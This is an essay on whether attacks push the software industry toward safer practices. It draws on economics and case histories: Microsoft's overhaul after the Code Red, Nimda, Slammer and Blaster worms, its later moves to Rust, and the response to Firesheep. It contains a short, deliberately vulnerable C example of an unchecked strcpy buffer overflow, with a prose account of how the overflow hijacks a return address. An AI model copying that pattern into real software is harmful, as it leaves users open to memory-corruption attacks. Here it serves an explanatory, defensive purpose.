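# Do attacks push industry to build safer software? The historical evidence

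## Why more attacks might or might not produce safer software

Most attacks on software begin with a vulnerability, a mistake in a program's code or design that an outsider can abuse. To do so, an attacker needs an exploit, which is a program or method that turns the vulnerability into a working attack. A zero-day is a vulnerability that attackers can use before the software's maker has a fix. Attack pressure is how often, how cheaply and how damagingly attackers hit a product or an industry.

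Attack pressure has been rising. *SoK* (2026), a survey of what AI models can do in vulnerability research, cites figures from the security firm Mandiant on the average time between the release of a patch and the first observed attack on the flaw. That time fell from 63 days in 2018 and 2019 to 5 days in 2023. The estimate for 2025 is minus 7 days, meaning that the first attack came, on average, a week before the patch.

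Many people in the field expect more attacks to do some good. A breach shows managers where their products are weak and what the weakness costs. Affected customers start asking for safer products. Managers then pay for work that their engineers had wanted to do for years, such as moving to safer programming languages. *Driven by AI, the Future of Cybersecurity Will Resemble the Past* (Healey, 2026) tells the history roughly this way. Worms, programs that copy themselves from machine to machine, caused over $250 billion of losses between 1999 and 2004 by one estimate (in 2025 dollars), and companies and policymakers then pushed Microsoft into large security changes. Healey also cites a forecast by Rob Joyce, a former White House cyber coordinator, that AI will be a "great cleansing forest fire" for old software. Until the fire has passed, Healey expects the main benefits of AI defence to go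 to two groups: defenders with the budgets and maturity to run it themselves, and those protected by the major AI companies and platforms. That protection is expected to be large but far from universal, with medical devices and home routers among the things likely to fall outside it.

In NYU Tandon's *With $1 Cyberattacks on the Rise, Durable Defenses Pay Off*, the computer scientists Justin Cappos and Evan Johnson contend that automated patching alone cannot counter AI-powered attacks that cost under a dollar, and that software needs safer foundations from the start. Runtime Verification, which sells mathematical proofs about code, makes a similar case for such proofs in *AI is making software harder to secure*.

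Even when engineers agree that safer foundations would help, their firms may not pay for them. *S3C2 Summit 2024-09* (Rahman, Acar and colleagues, 2025) reports on a closed-door meeting of 12 practitioners from 9 companies, all of whom agreed that languages such as Rust and Go could help. It adds that the switch can bring significant overhead and be hard to sell to senior leadership. A blog post excerpted in LWN's *Vulnerability Research Is Cooked* describes the industry in 2026 as already convinced but slow to switch.

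### What a memory-safety flaw is, and what prevents it

A memory-safety flaw is an error that lets a program read or write memory it should not. Such errors are common in C and C++, the languages of most operating systems. A C program that greets visitors by name might contain these lines:

```c
char name[16];
strcpy(name, input);
```

The declaration of `name` sets aside 16 bytes of memory. `strcpy` then copies all of the visitor's input there without checking its length. If the visitor sends 200 bytes, the copy overwrites memory beyond the reserved space, a flaw called a buffer overflow. The overwritten memory can include the return address, which tells the processor where to go when the current piece of code finishes. An attacker can choose the 200 bytes to put a different address there and so take over the program. Other memory-safety flaws include reading past the end of a buffer, which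 can leak secrets, and using memory after the program has released it.

Memory-safe languages, such as Rust, Java, Go and Swift, have rules that prevent most of these errors. In a Rust example from a conference talk (AI Engineer, 2026), a program holds a packet of three bytes and tries to read a fourth. Rust returns a value meaning "nothing there", which the programmer must handle, and the program never reads memory outside the packet. Rust allows exceptions in marked sections, known as unsafe Rust, where the programmer must guarantee memory safety instead of the compiler. The speaker, Cable, cited estimates that memory-safe languages could prevent about 60–70% of the vulnerabilities in products written in languages that are not memory-safe, and Microsoft has given a similar figure for its own products.

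Some kinds of vulnerability would survive a change of programming language. *Vulnerability Abundance* (Leverett and van der Ham-de Vos, 2026) presents a C program that generates vulnerabilities without limit, starting from eleven textbook flaws. At least three of the eleven could occur in any language: passing a user's input to the operating system as a command, letting a user name a file outside the permitted folder, and leaving a gap between checking a file and using it.

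Formal verification goes further, using a machine-checked mathematical proof to show that code meets a written specification, which is an exact statement of what the code should do. Testing tries a program on some inputs, while a proof covers all the inputs that the specification describes. *Escaping the Quicksand* (Sewell and Pichon-Pharabod, 2026) points out that a program that takes a single megabyte of input has far more possible inputs than the observable universe has atoms. A proof can also rule out errors unrelated to memory, such as cryptographic code that leaks its keys or login logic that lets attackers around access controls (*How Could Formal Verification Help with Cyber Resilience?*). Researchers have proved properties of whole systems this way, including the operating-system kernel seL4.

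A proof shows only that software meets its specification, though, and the specification can be wrong. *After Cheap Discovery* (Sistany, 2026) describes two ways this can happen. If the designers trusted the wrong component and wrote that trust into the specification, the proof will not reveal the mistake. A team facing a deadline can also weaken the specification until the proof succeeds, which looks like engineering judgement and is hard to spot. *SoK* rates the evidence for memory-safe languages as a defence "strong". It rates the evidence for formal verification with AI models "weak", because that evidence consists of one vendor's proofs that certain functions do not crash on inputs of limited size.

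Secure defaults deal with settings instead of code. A home router that ships with remote administration switched off and a different password on each unit protects owners who never open the settings page. The remote-administration code may still contain a bug, but outsiders cannot reach it. In *Why Information Security is Hard* (2001), the Cambridge computer scientist Ross Anderson described the opposite arrangement in Windows NT, which had access controls that often made no difference because most applications ran with administrator privileges or the equivalent. The phrase "secure by design" covers both building a product so that whole classes of flaws cannot arise and shipping it with safe settings switched on.

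### Repair, hardening, prevention

A company under attack can respond at three levels. Repair means fixing the flaw somebody found, for instance by adding a length check to the greeting program. Hardening means making flaws harder to exploit while leaving them in place. MIT's *Memory safety is at a tipping point* describes two Lincoln Laboratory products that reshuffle the location of a program's code in memory each time the program accesses it. An attacker who can overwrite a return address then doesn't know which address to write. Prevention means building code in a way that eliminates the class of flaw, for instance by writing a new component in Rust.

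Anderson gave an arithmetical reason to care about depth. Suppose a large product has a million bugs, and a tester needs a billion hours on average to find any particular one. An attacker who spends 1,000 hours a year finds about one bug a year. A defender who spends ten million hours finds about 10,000, or 1% of the total. (Anderson wrote 100,000, ten times what the inputs give.) The chance that the defender has already fixed the attacker's bug is therefore about one in a hundred, despite ten thousand times the effort. Anderson saw two serious solutions. One was to make a single change that removes many bugs at once, such as a new compiler that eliminates stack overflows. The other was to shrink the security-critical part of the system until people can check all of it.

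Whether repairing flaws makes software safer depends partly on how many flaws there are, and the evidence on that is mixed. Leverett and van der Ham-de Vos recount the security researcher Dan Geer's framing of the debate, in which each repair reduces exposure if flaws are sparse, but one more repair is "essentially irrelevant to security" if they are dense. A study of the OpenBSD operating system over seven and a half years found that reports of flaws in its original code slowed, though the median flaw lived at least 2.6 years. A study of two web servers found no such slowing. Repairs probably do improve security in old code that changes little, but most commercial products keep adding new code, and new flaws with it.

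### Three economic reasons for doubt

Anderson's main claim was that insecurity comes at least as much from bad incentives as from bad technology, and the leading example was cash-machine fraud. In the United States, when a customer disputed a withdrawal, the bank had to prove the customer wrong. In Britain, Norway and the Netherlands, the customer had to prove the bank wrong, which was nearly impossible, so banks there grew careless. Economists call this kind of cost, which falls on someone other than the decision-maker, an externality. American banks spent less on security but spent it better, and they suffered much less fraud. The example also gives some support to the view that attacks improve security, since Anderson reports that "epidemics of fraud" eventually ended the European banks' complacency, though only after customers had paid for much of the fraud. The banking systems differed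 in other ways too, so the comparison supports the claim about incentives but doesn't measure how much they mattered.

In software, too, losses often fall on people other than those who could prevent them. When the SQL Slammer worm exploited a flaw in a Microsoft product in January 2003, the investment bank where Healey worked cut itself off from the internet for a week and suffered millions of dollars in damage. Sewell and Pichon-Pharabod write that the risks of fast development fall largely on users and society. *Funding Formal Methods for the Cyberpocalypse*, a 2026 essay, lists industrial control systems and the software of small banks and hospitals among products whose makers have too little reason to harden them. Users also neglect security when others bear the loss. Anderson cites the economist Hal Varian's observation that people will spend $100 on anti-virus software for themselves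 but hardly $1 to stop attackers from using their computers against Amazon.

Customers could push vendors to build safer software by buying the safer product, if they could tell which one it was. *The Market for "Lemons"* (Akerlof, 1970) shows how a market can collapse when buyers cannot judge quality. In its example, the quality of used cars is spread evenly from 0 to 2. An owner values a car at exactly its quality, and a buyer values it at one and a half times that, so every car should sell. But at any price P, up to the value of the best car, owners offer only cars of quality below P. These cars have an average quality of P/2 and are worth an average of 0.75P to buyers, who therefore refuse to pay P. This happens at every price, so no cars sell.

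Anderson applied the idea to security products, and Ozment (2004), in *Bug Auctions*, notes that people have compared the market for secure software to a market for lemons because security is hard to measure. The comparison is imperfect because the owner of a bad car knows it is bad, while the maker of a million-line program may have little idea how many flaws it contains. Sistany argues that cheap AI scanning is removing this difference, since the vendor now has a list of the known flaws it has decided to ship, which the buyer cannot see. Outside certification is the usual remedy, but Anderson had a low opinion of the main scheme, the Common Criteria, in which the vendor pays the evaluator and can choose the most lenient one.

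Lock-in also weakens the pressure that attacks put on vendors. Software markets reward whoever arrives first, because users want what other users have. Anderson thought it "perfectly rational" in such markets to ship early and get the product right by version 3. Once customers have built their business around a product, leaving is expensive, so the vendor loses little when attackers hit them. Vendors are also locked into old designs. Sewell and Pichon-Pharabod trace today's systems to design choices of the 1960s and 1970s, when attacks were almost unknown, and consider wholesale replacement infeasible because the installed base is so large. Some of those systems can't feasibly be repaired either. Cybersecurity Dive quotes Joyce, who elsewhere forecast the cleansing fire, on how much technology is unsupported, outdated or without anyone to install a patch.

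### A rule for when a firm changes its practice

These considerations fit into one inequality. A firm adopts a safer practice if

r·s·p·L + b > C

where p is the yearly chance of a serious attack, L is the total loss such an attack causes to everyone, s is the share of that loss the firm itself bears, r is the share of the loss that the practice would prevent, b is any other yearly benefit, such as faster development, and C is the yearly cost.

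Suppose L is $100 million, r is 0.7, and there are no other benefits, so b = 0.

| Firm's share of loss (s) | Yearly chance of attack (p) | Yearly benefit to firm | Yearly cost (C) | Adopts? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 10% | 2% | $0.14m | $5m | No |
| 10% | 20% | $1.4m | $5m | No |
| 50% | 2% | $0.7m | $5m | No |
| 50% | 20% | $7m | $5m | Yes |
| 10% | 20% | $1.4m | $1m | Yes |

A tenfold rise in attacks would not lead a firm that bears a tenth of the loss to adopt the practice. At a cost of $5 million, the practice pays for itself only if that firm faces at least a 71% yearly chance of a serious attack. For a firm that bears half the loss, the threshold is 14%. Cutting the cost to $1 million also lowers the first firm's threshold to 14%, so a fivefold fall in cost has the same effect as a fivefold rise in liability. If the practice saved a firm more than $5 million a year in developers' time,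 the firm would adopt it even with no attacks.

At a 2% chance of attack, the practice costs $5 million and saves everyone together $1.4 million a year, so refusing it is the right decision. At 20%, it saves $14 million a year, but the firm with the 10% share still refuses it, which is a market failure.

Each of the three doubts concerns particular terms. Vendors that bear little of the loss have a low s. Hidden quality also keeps s low, because buyers do not punish vendors for flaws they cannot see, and it lowers b by removing the extra sales a safer product might have earned. Lock-in raises C for old code and lowers s for vendors whose customers cannot switch.

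Cheaper alternatives matter as much as any of these. Suppose the firm that bears half the loss could instead buy hardening that prevents 40% of the loss for $0.5 million a year. At a 20% chance of attack, hardening yields a net $3.5 million and prevention a net $2 million, so the firm hardens. Prevention is the better buy only when the chance of attack exceeds 30%. More attacks can change a firm's behaviour without leading it to remove the class of flaw.

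The rule's simplifications mostly make prevention look better than it is. The 0.7 resembles the share of flaws that memory-safe languages might prevent, but r is a share of losses. Attackers ever use fewer than 6% of published vulnerabilities, by the estimates that Leverett and van der Ham-de Vos collect, and attackers who can't use one flaw may use another. Attack pressure can also raise C, because the people who would rebuild the product are busy patching it. Sistany cites Verizon data showing that the workload from flaws attackers were already using grew 78% in a year, while the share of those flaws that organisations fully fixed fell from 38% to 26%. Those organisations were running software rather than writing it, so the figures only suggest what happens inside a vendor. On the other hand, managers act on their own estimate of p, and a breach can correct an estimate that was too low.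 The idea that companies learn from losses is sound to that extent.

### Telling attacks from other causes

A safer practice adopted after an attack may have other causes. Five checks help show whether the attack led to it: timing, stated reasons, comparable firms, depth of change and rival causes.

Timing is the easiest test to apply. If attacks caused a change, its budget, hiring and first prototypes should come after them. An attack can at most have sped up a project that was already under way. Stated reasons help when they date from the time of the decision and come from people who had to justify the spending. Later speeches are weaker evidence, because a company has reason to credit security when talking to customers and a pleasant programming language when recruiting programmers.

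Comparisons between similar firms are the strongest evidence. If attackers hit several similar companies and only one rebuilt its product, attacks alone were not enough, and something about that company made the difference. In the cash-machine comparison, the difference was liability. Firms that changed without any attack are also useful evidence, since they show that attacks were not necessary. Famous cases tend to be those where something changed afterwards, so firms that were attacked and carried on as before are easy to miss.

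Firms may respond to attacks with a burst of patches or with a lasting change in how they build software. Vulnerability counts are a poor way to tell the two apart, because they rise when people look harder, regardless of the code's quality. Better evidence is the share of new code a firm writes using safer methods, and whether it still uses them years after the attacks were in the news.

Causes other than attacks change the other terms of the rule. A law that makes vendors liable raises s, and so does a customer large enough to threaten to leave. Better tools lower C, and a language that lets programmers work faster raises b. Several terms often change in the same years, and then the evidence can show at most that attacks were one of several causes.

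## Windows worms and Microsoft's security overhaul, 2001–2004

The first worm to do serious damage on the internet changed very little about how programmers wrote code. In November 1988 Robert Morris, a graduate student, released a worm that broke into computers running Unix. It got into some of them through a buffer overflow, the same kind of error as in the greeting program above. A bug made the worm copy itself onto the same machine hundreds of times until the machine crashed. Roughly a tenth of the American computers on the internet stopped working, according to *Information Security* (2001), testimony to Congress by GAO, the US government's audit office. The US government responded by funding the CERT Coordination Center, a team at Carnegie Mellon University that handles reports of attacks and vulnerabilities, but programmers kept writing Unix in C.

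Eight years later a hacker writing as Aleph One published "Smashing the Stack for Fun and Profit" in the online magazine *Phrack*. The tutorial showed readers, step by step, how to overflow a buffer, overwrite the return address, and point it at instructions hidden in the input. Anyone who could program in C could now learn the technique, but programmers went on writing operating systems and servers in C and C++.

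Memory-safe languages did spread in those years, but in other kinds of software and mostly for other reasons. Sun Microsystems released Java in 1996, and Microsoft released C# in 2002. Security was one of Java's selling points, because web browsers had to run Java programs written by strangers. Businesses adopted it largely because the same program ran on any make of computer and because programmers no longer had to release memory by hand. A routine called a garbage collector did that for them, but it made programs slower and used more memory. Microsoft (2019) gave this overhead as the reason why operating-system kernels and networking code stayed with languages that are not memory-safe. In terms of the rule above, b was large for a payroll program, but C was prohibitive for a kernel.

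### Code Red, Nimda and the halt in Windows development

Microsoft began working on security before the worms of 2001. *Inside the Secure Windows Initiative* (Howard, 2000) described a central group that offered product teams training, tools and advice. Steve Lipner, who took over the group in 2001, recalled in Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft's Steve Lipner* that it started with two or three people, whose job was to review all the code in Windows and find the security bugs. He called this "a completely naive approach".

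In July 2001, the Code Red worm exploited a buffer overflow in Internet Information Server (IIS), Microsoft's web server. Microsoft had released a patch the month before. On 19 July the worm infected more than 359,000 computers in under 14 hours (Moore, Shannon and Brown, *Code-Red*, 2002). The Pentagon briefly shut down its public websites, and the worm reportedly got into Hotmail, Microsoft's email service.

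Nimda followed on 18 September. According to CERT/CC's *CERT Advisory CA-2001-26 Nimda Worm* (2001), it spread through email, shared network folders, infected web pages, and a flaw in IIS that let outsiders reach files beyond the permitted folder. None of these routes relied on a buffer overflow, so a Windows written entirely in a memory-safe language would still have been vulnerable.

Within days the analyst firm Gartner advised companies hit by both worms to look immediately for alternatives to IIS, and to hold off on .NET products that relied on IIS until Microsoft had completely rewritten the server. The Register's *Ditch Microsoft IIS now, says Gartner* (2001) called this unusually blunt for a firm with "enormous clout at board level". Gartner argued that patches arriving "almost weekly" made IIS more expensive to own, as Redmond Channel Partner's *Gartner* (2001) reported. A Microsoft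 spokesman replied in IT World Canada that every web server had had serious flaws, and some users blamed administrators who had not installed the patches.

The reply did not settle the matter, even inside Microsoft. Cherry (2001) reports in *Get Secure, Stay Secure* that the Windows division spent the next two weeks reviewing its security tools and holding conference calls with key customers. Microsoft then released tools that helped customers lock down their servers and install patches. In November and December, the .NET runtime team of one to two thousand people worked only on security until it thought the product was fit to ship. Lipner's group drew up a similar plan for Windows.

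On 15 January 2002 Bill Gates, then Microsoft's chief software architect, sent all employees a memo titled "Trustworthy computing". He wrote that when new features and security conflicted, "we need to choose security". In *Gates Puts Focus on Trustworthy Computing*, Cherry (2002) counted this as Microsoft's third security initiative in a year and considered it more likely to succeed than the others because it came from the top. The Register printed the memo in full and suspected it was a "PR smokescreen".

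Lipner said in *Interview with Microsoft's Steve Lipner* that about four trainers taught 8,500 people to write secure code in the last week of January, filling a 950-seat room ten times. From 1 February, everyone who worked on Windows stopped adding features and instead listed ways to attack each component, reviewed code, and looked for services they could switch off or run with fewer privileges. A database recorded which developer had signed off each file. Sample code got the highest priority because customers copied it into their own programs. Gates had expected the halt to last 30 days. InternetNews' *Microsoft Spent $100M on Trustworthy Computing* reports that it took nearly twice as long and cost over $100 million. The SQL Server, Exchange and Office teams did the same in turn until the summer.

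As a result of the halt, Microsoft hardened its new server system by compiling it with an option called GS, which places a secret value in memory between a function's buffers and its return address. In the greeting program, a visitor's 200 bytes would overwrite that value on their way to the return address. The program checks the value before it uses the address and stops if it has changed. The overflow is still there and an attacker can still use it to crash the program, but taking control is much harder. Lipner pointed out to Stevenson that programs running on .NET could not contain such overruns at all. Microsoft had a memory-safe language on the market in the same month that it halted Windows development, but chose to review the C and C++ code instead of replacing it.

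### Slammer, Blaster and Service Pack 2

Microsoft put some of the changes from the security reviews into service packs, or bundles of fixes, for software that customers already ran: Windows XP, SQL Server 2000 and Exchange 2000. The changes to Windows were most extensive in a new product, Windows Server 2003. At its launch, MCPmag's *Viewpoint* (2003) predicted that such systems would need several years to make up even half of the servers in use. Two more worms spread in 2003 through machines without the latest patches.

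| Worm | Date | Way in | Age of the patch | Damage estimates |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Code Red | July 2001 | Buffer overflow in IIS | About 1 month | $2.62bn; $2.75bn |
| Nimda | September 2001 | Several, including an IIS file-path flaw | About 11 months (IIS flaw) | $0.68bn; $1.50bn |
| SQL Slammer | January 2003 | Buffer overflow in SQL Server | About 6 months | $1.05bn; $1.25bn |
| Blaster | August 2003 | Buffer overflow in a Windows network service | Almost 1 month | $0.53bn or more |

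The paired estimates come from two consulting firms, Mi2g and Computer Economics, and deserve little trust. According to the Congressional Research Service's *The Economic Impact of Cyber-Attacks*, both firms sold security services and kept their models secret. Their estimates for SoBig, a 2003 email worm, were $30.91 billion and $1.10 billion. The Blaster figure comes from a U.S. House hearing.

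Slammer infected more than 90% of vulnerable machines within ten minutes, and the network congestion it caused put cash machines out of service and led airlines to cancel flights. Blaster spread more slowly but further. TechSpot's *Blaster worm could have infected over 8 million PCs* reported Microsoft data showing at least 8 million infected PCs. The worm attacked Windows 2000 and XP, but Windows Server 2003 had the same flaw. This was embarrassing for Microsoft, because thousands of engineers had spent two months reviewing that product during the halt without finding it.

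In all four cases a patch existed, but many customers had not installed it. To make patches easier to handle, Microsoft began releasing them on a fixed day each month in 2003, a change that its *Celebrating 20 Years of Trustworthy Computing* (2022) credits with making updates more predictable. Its larger response was Windows XP Service Pack 2, a free update released in August 2004 and meant to protect computers even without the latest patches. Microsoft's *Here's why SP2 is such an important update for Windows XP* says that recent worms had made it "a much more security-centric update than was originally planned".

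Windows XP already had a firewall, which blocks connections the user did not ask for, but it was off unless the user turned it on. The most important change in Service Pack 2 was to turn it on by default and keep ports closed except when a program was using them (Andersen and Abella, 2004, *Changes to Functionality in Windows XP Service Pack 2*). A worm like Blaster, which arrived as an unrequested connection, could no longer reach the flawed service on most home computers. Part 2 of the same guide describes two little-used messaging services that the update disabled and a new rule that only administrators could start certain Windows components from another machine. The network service that Blaster had attacked now ran with fewer privileges, so an attacker who got in could do less.

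For the same update, Microsoft also recompiled core Windows components with the GS option and added support for data execution prevention, in which the processor refuses to run instructions from memory marked as holding data. This stops an attacker from running instructions placed in a buffer, the method taught in the 1996 tutorial. Few processors had the feature in 2004.

### What the Security Development Lifecycle requires

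The 2002 halt was an emergency measure, carried out late in development because Windows had already reached that stage. The Security Development Lifecycle (SDL) spread the same work over a product's whole life. Senior managers approved it in 2004, after chief executive Steve Ballmer told them that Microsoft was going to do it and would not discuss it any more. It took effect on 1 July.

*The Trustworthy Computing Security Development Lifecycle* (Lipner and Howard, 2005) describes the steps that a team building a mail server, for example, would follow. Its engineers attend security training every year. When planning begins, the central security team assigns them an adviser, or "security buddy". At the design stage, the engineers document the attack surface (everything an outsider can reach) and turn off by default whatever most customers will not use. They also write a threat model listing,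 for each component, what an attacker might want, how they could get at it and what would stop them.

While writing the code, the team uses safer functions to handle text and buffers. It runs static-analysis tools, which search the code for mistakes without running it, and fuzzers, which feed the program malformed input to see whether it breaks. Engineers also review the code by hand, since the tools miss some mistakes. Once the server is complete and in public testing, the team holds a "security push", a second round of review and testing that includes code from earlier versions.

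Two to six months before release, the central team carries out a Final Security Review. It interviews the developers, rechecks bugs they had dismissed as harmless and, for a major product, tries to break into it. If the reviewers find a pattern of flaws, the team must also fix the cause, such as poor training or a weak tool. After release, the team investigates each vulnerability outsiders report and looks for others like it.

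These rules were mandatory for any product that handled personal data, ran in an organisation or connected to a network. Howard said they covered about 90% of Microsoft's products in an interview for Naraine's *Microsoft Claims Security Win with New Development Rules* (2005). Games for very young children were exempt. Lipner and Howard include strongly typed languages, a category that includes Java and C#, among the techniques designers might consider, but the SDL did not require any team to use one.

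### What the bulletin counts measure

Microsoft published a comparison early in 2004, after Windows Server 2003 had been on sale for 320 days. It counted security bulletins, the notices that accompany patches, and for Windows it included only those that Microsoft rated critical or important.

| Product | Period compared | Before | After |
|---|---|---|---|
| Windows 2000 Server against Windows Server 2003 | First 320 days on sale | 40 | 9 |
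| SQL Server 2000, before and after Service Pack 3 | 15 months each side | 13 | 3 |
| Exchange 2000, before and after Service Pack 3 | 21 months each side | 7 | 1 |

Microsoft added that the new version of IIS, the server Gartner had told companies to abandon, had needed no bulletins in nearly a year. After two years it had needed only one, for a component not installed by default, which was a large improvement on the earlier "almost weekly" rate.

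The totals are less convincing as evidence about the quality of the code. A bulletin can cover several flaws, and CERIAS's *What security push?*, a 2007 critique from Purdue University's security research centre, points out that bundled patches hide how many there are. Severity ratings depend on defaults, so a flaw in a service that Microsoft had switched off may drop out of the count even though the code is unchanged. Customers do benefit, but from hardening rather than better code. Windows Server 2003 was also new and had few users, which gave attackers less reason to study it. For SQL Server and Exchange, the comparison is between younger code and the same code after outsiders had spent years finding its flaws, so reports might have fallen anyway.

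The Windows gap also narrowed. By March 2005 Naraine was reporting 62 bulletins for Windows 2000 and 24 for Windows Server 2003, a ratio of 2.6, down from 4.4 in the earlier figures, though the two comparisons may cover different periods. Lipner and Howard themselves thought it premature to claim conclusively that the SDL worked.

Attackers' later behavior is better evidence. Matt Miller, a Microsoft security engineer, showed that most vulnerabilities Microsoft patched between 2006 and 2019 had no known exploit within 30 days of the patch (Miller 2020). When attackers did exploit one, they most often used it first as a zero-day against chosen targets. *Trends and Challenges in the Vulnerability Mitigation Landscape* (Miller 2019) describes the typical attack changing over twenty years from an easy stack overflow to an expensive chain of several exploits. Miller credits the accumulated hardening.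 He works for Microsoft, and attackers by then also had more profitable options than writing worms, but the trend he describes fits the historical record.

### The 70% that stayed

In July 2019 Microsoft reported that memory-safety flaws accounted for about 70% of the vulnerabilities it fixed and gave a public identifier each year, "despite mitigations including intense code review, training, static analysis, and more". Microsoft (2019) found that the proportion had hardly changed in over a decade and concluded that tools and guidance were "demonstrably not preventing" such flaws. The 70% figure changed how people in the field talked about the SDL.

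The constant 70% share alone doesn't show whether the number of memory-safety flaws fell, because the SDL could have halved them along with all other flaws. But Microsoft's *A proactive approach to more secure code* (2019) says that the problem was getting worse as the company's code base grew. The SDL's tools and rules particularly targeted buffer overflows, so the share should have fallen if the process had worked as hoped, but it did not fall in fifteen years.

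The Conficker worm infected millions of computers from November 2008 through a buffer overflow in a Windows network service, which Microsoft had patched about a month earlier. The flaw was in Windows XP, Windows Server 2003 and Vista, so Microsoft had missed it both during the 2002 halt in Windows development and under its Security Development Lifecycle (SDL). On Vista, however, an attacker normally had to log in before reaching the flaw, and on XP the default firewall blocked the worm's main route unless the user had allowed an exception, for instance to share files. Conficker also spread by guessing weak passwords and through USB sticks.

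In May 2017, WannaCry encrypted files on more than 200,000 computers in some 150 countries and demanded ransom, forcing British hospitals to turn patients away. It used EternalBlue, an exploit that the US National Security Agency had developed and a group calling itself the Shadow Brokers had leaked. The exploit attacked memory-safety errors in Windows' code for an old file-sharing protocol, SMBv1. Microsoft had released a patch two months before the attack, and WannaCry's version of the exploit did not work on Windows 10 because of later hardening. Microsoft had urged customers in 2016 to stop using SMBv1, and in autumn 2017 it stopped installing the protocol by default on new copies of Windows. It again changed a default but did not change the programming language.

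### Rust at Microsoft

The 2019 posts recommended Rust as the best available alternative to C and C++ because it offers memory safety without a garbage collector. Adoption has been slow since. In 2022 Mark Russinovich, the chief technology officer of Microsoft's cloud service Azure, called on the industry to stop starting new projects in C and C++. In 2023 Microsoft shipped about 36,000 lines of Rust in the Windows kernel's graphics code, and it had also rewritten much of a library for displaying text in Rust. In 2025 its researchers announced that they were rewriting parts of SymCrypt, the company's main cryptographic library, in Rust and proving them correct.

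Windows has tens of millions of lines of code, so these are small pieces of it. In December 2025 Galen Hunt, a senior Microsoft engineer, described in a job advertisement a goal of eliminating all of the company's C and C++ code by 2030 with the help of AI. After the press reported this as a plan to rewrite Windows, Hunt explained that the advertisement described a research project and that Windows was not being rewritten in Rust. At the start of 2026, Windows was still a C and C++ system with Rust in selected components. By then Google's Android, which had made Rust a standard choice for new system code, had reduced memory-safety flaws to less than 20% of its vulnerabilities.

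### Did the worms cause the change?

The timing mostly fits the idea that the worms drove Microsoft's overhaul, though some of the work began earlier. The Secure Windows Initiative was a year and a half old when Code Red appeared, and the .NET team had its own reasons to check a product it was about to launch. After the worms, the effort grew from a handful of reviewers to 8,500 people in a little over six months.

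The people responsible also gave the worms as their reason as early as 2002, when Lipner told Stevenson that Code Red and Nimda had prompted a short-term response, and that the question of how to "get ahead of this" had led "to a large part" to the Trustworthy Computing initiative. This admission is more believable because Microsoft would have looked better crediting its own foresight. Lipner later recalled "a lot of embarrassment and a lot of customer upset". He also mentioned the attacks of 11 September 2001, a week before Nimda, as part of the background, and their influence cannot be separated from that of the worms.

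Other attacked software did not change in this way. The Morris worm hit machines made by Digital and Sun, and neither firm halted development. In September 2002 the Slapper worm broke into Linux web servers through a buffer overflow in OpenSSL, a free encryption library, whose few developers fixed the flaw and carried on. Unlike them, Microsoft had large corporate customers, a platform to sell them that depended on the server Gartner had condemned, and $100 million to spend. No law made Microsoft pay for its customers' losses, but Gartner's advice threatened its sales, which raised its share of the loss, s. The attacks probably influenced Microsoft mainly through its customers.

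Microsoft also bore some costs directly. During the worms, it bused engineers to its support centre to help answer calls, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Worms and Wildly Insecure Software*. A Microsoft employee told the CERIAS critic that responding to a major flaw often cost close to $1 million. If every bulletin cost that much, the fall from 72 bulletins in 2002 to 45 in 2004 saved $27 million a year, and the halt would have paid for itself in about four years. The $1 million figure is hearsay, and the calculation leaves out the continuing cost of the SDL, but it suggests the overhaul may have been a reasonable investment even without the threat to sales.

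Microsoft's changes lasted, and the SDL was still mandatory long after the worms had left the news. But the changes were limited to hardening and a stricter process. There was little prospect of going further at the time, because garbage collection was impractical in kernel code and Rust had no stable release until 2015. When Microsoft made the case for changing languages, two years after WannaCry, it relied mainly on its own vulnerability records going back to 2004.

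## Two easy web attacks with different outcomes: Firesheep and SQL injection

Unlike writing a Windows worm, attacking websites with Firesheep or SQL injection took almost no skill, and a memory-safe language would have stopped neither attack. Firesheep, a browser add-on from 2010, let anyone on an open Wi-Fi network take over other people's logged-in accounts. SQL injection lets an attacker run commands on a website's database by typing them into a form. In both cases, engineers knew a good fix years before the most famous attacks. The weakness behind Firesheep has almost disappeared from the public web, but software makers still ship products with SQL injection flaws.

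### How Firesheep took over accounts

When a user logs in to a website, the site checks the password and sends back a cookie, a short piece of text that the browser attaches to every later request. The site treats anyone who presents the cookie as the logged-in user. In 2010 many websites encrypted the login but sent everything after it, including the cookie, over HTTP, which has no encryption. On an open Wi-Fi network every laptop in range can pick up that traffic, so anyone nearby could copy a cookie and use the account. HTTPS prevents this by encrypting the connection, and the encryption behind it dates from 1994.

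A security specialist told Krebs on Security (2010) that people in the field had talked about the problem since at least 2003. In 2008, a researcher showed a tool for hijacking Gmail accounts this way at a hacker conference. According to Zscaler's *Detecting Firesheep*, that tool got some press, but the industry did little about it.

The programmer Eric Butler released the add-on Firesheep on 24 October 2010 and described it in codebutler's *Firesheep* (2010). When the user clicked a button, a sidebar showed the names and photos of people on the same network who were visiting vulnerable sites. Double-clicking on a person opened that person's account. The add-on covered about 25 services, including Amazon, Facebook, Twitter and Yahoo. Butler said he wanted to make people demand better from websites that had ignored a "widely known problem". In *Firesheep* (2010), Butler and Gallagher counted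 919,997 downloads by early December.

Some of the first responses did not address the underlying problem, which was that websites were still sending cookies unencrypted. Butler and Gallagher complained that news reports told readers to avoid open Wi-Fi, and that anti-virus companies had started to block Firesheep itself.

### What Gmail, Facebook and Twitter did

| Service | Optional HTTPS for the whole session | HTTPS by default for everyone | Default relative to Firesheep |
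|---|---|---|---|
| Gmail | 2008 | January 2010 | 9 months before |
| Twitter | March 2011 | February 2012 | 16 months after |
| Facebook | January 2011 | July 2013 | 33 months after |

Firesheep therefore did not cause Gmail's switch to HTTPS by default. In June 2009, 37 academics asked Google's chief executive to consider encrypting Gmail by default, and Google replied that free, always-on HTTPS was "pretty unusual in the email business" (Silicon Republic, *Gmail goes HTTPS by default*, 2010). Google had left HTTPS optional because it could make mail slower. In *Default https access for Gmail*, Schillace (2010) explained that the company had spent the previous few months studying the trade-off and now thought the security was worth the delay.

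That announcement came on 12 January 2010, the same day that Google disclosed a break-in from China. The break-in may have hurried the decision, but the academics' letter and the months of testing are enough to explain it. eWeek's *Twitter Enables HTTPS for All Users* (2012) treats the break-in as the reason for the change, but Google detected the attack only in mid-December, and its review of HTTPS seems to have started earlier. HTTPS would not have helped much either. Google explained in a March update to *A new approach to China* (2010) that outsiders had most likely got into activists' Gmail accounts through phishing or malware on the activists' own computers.

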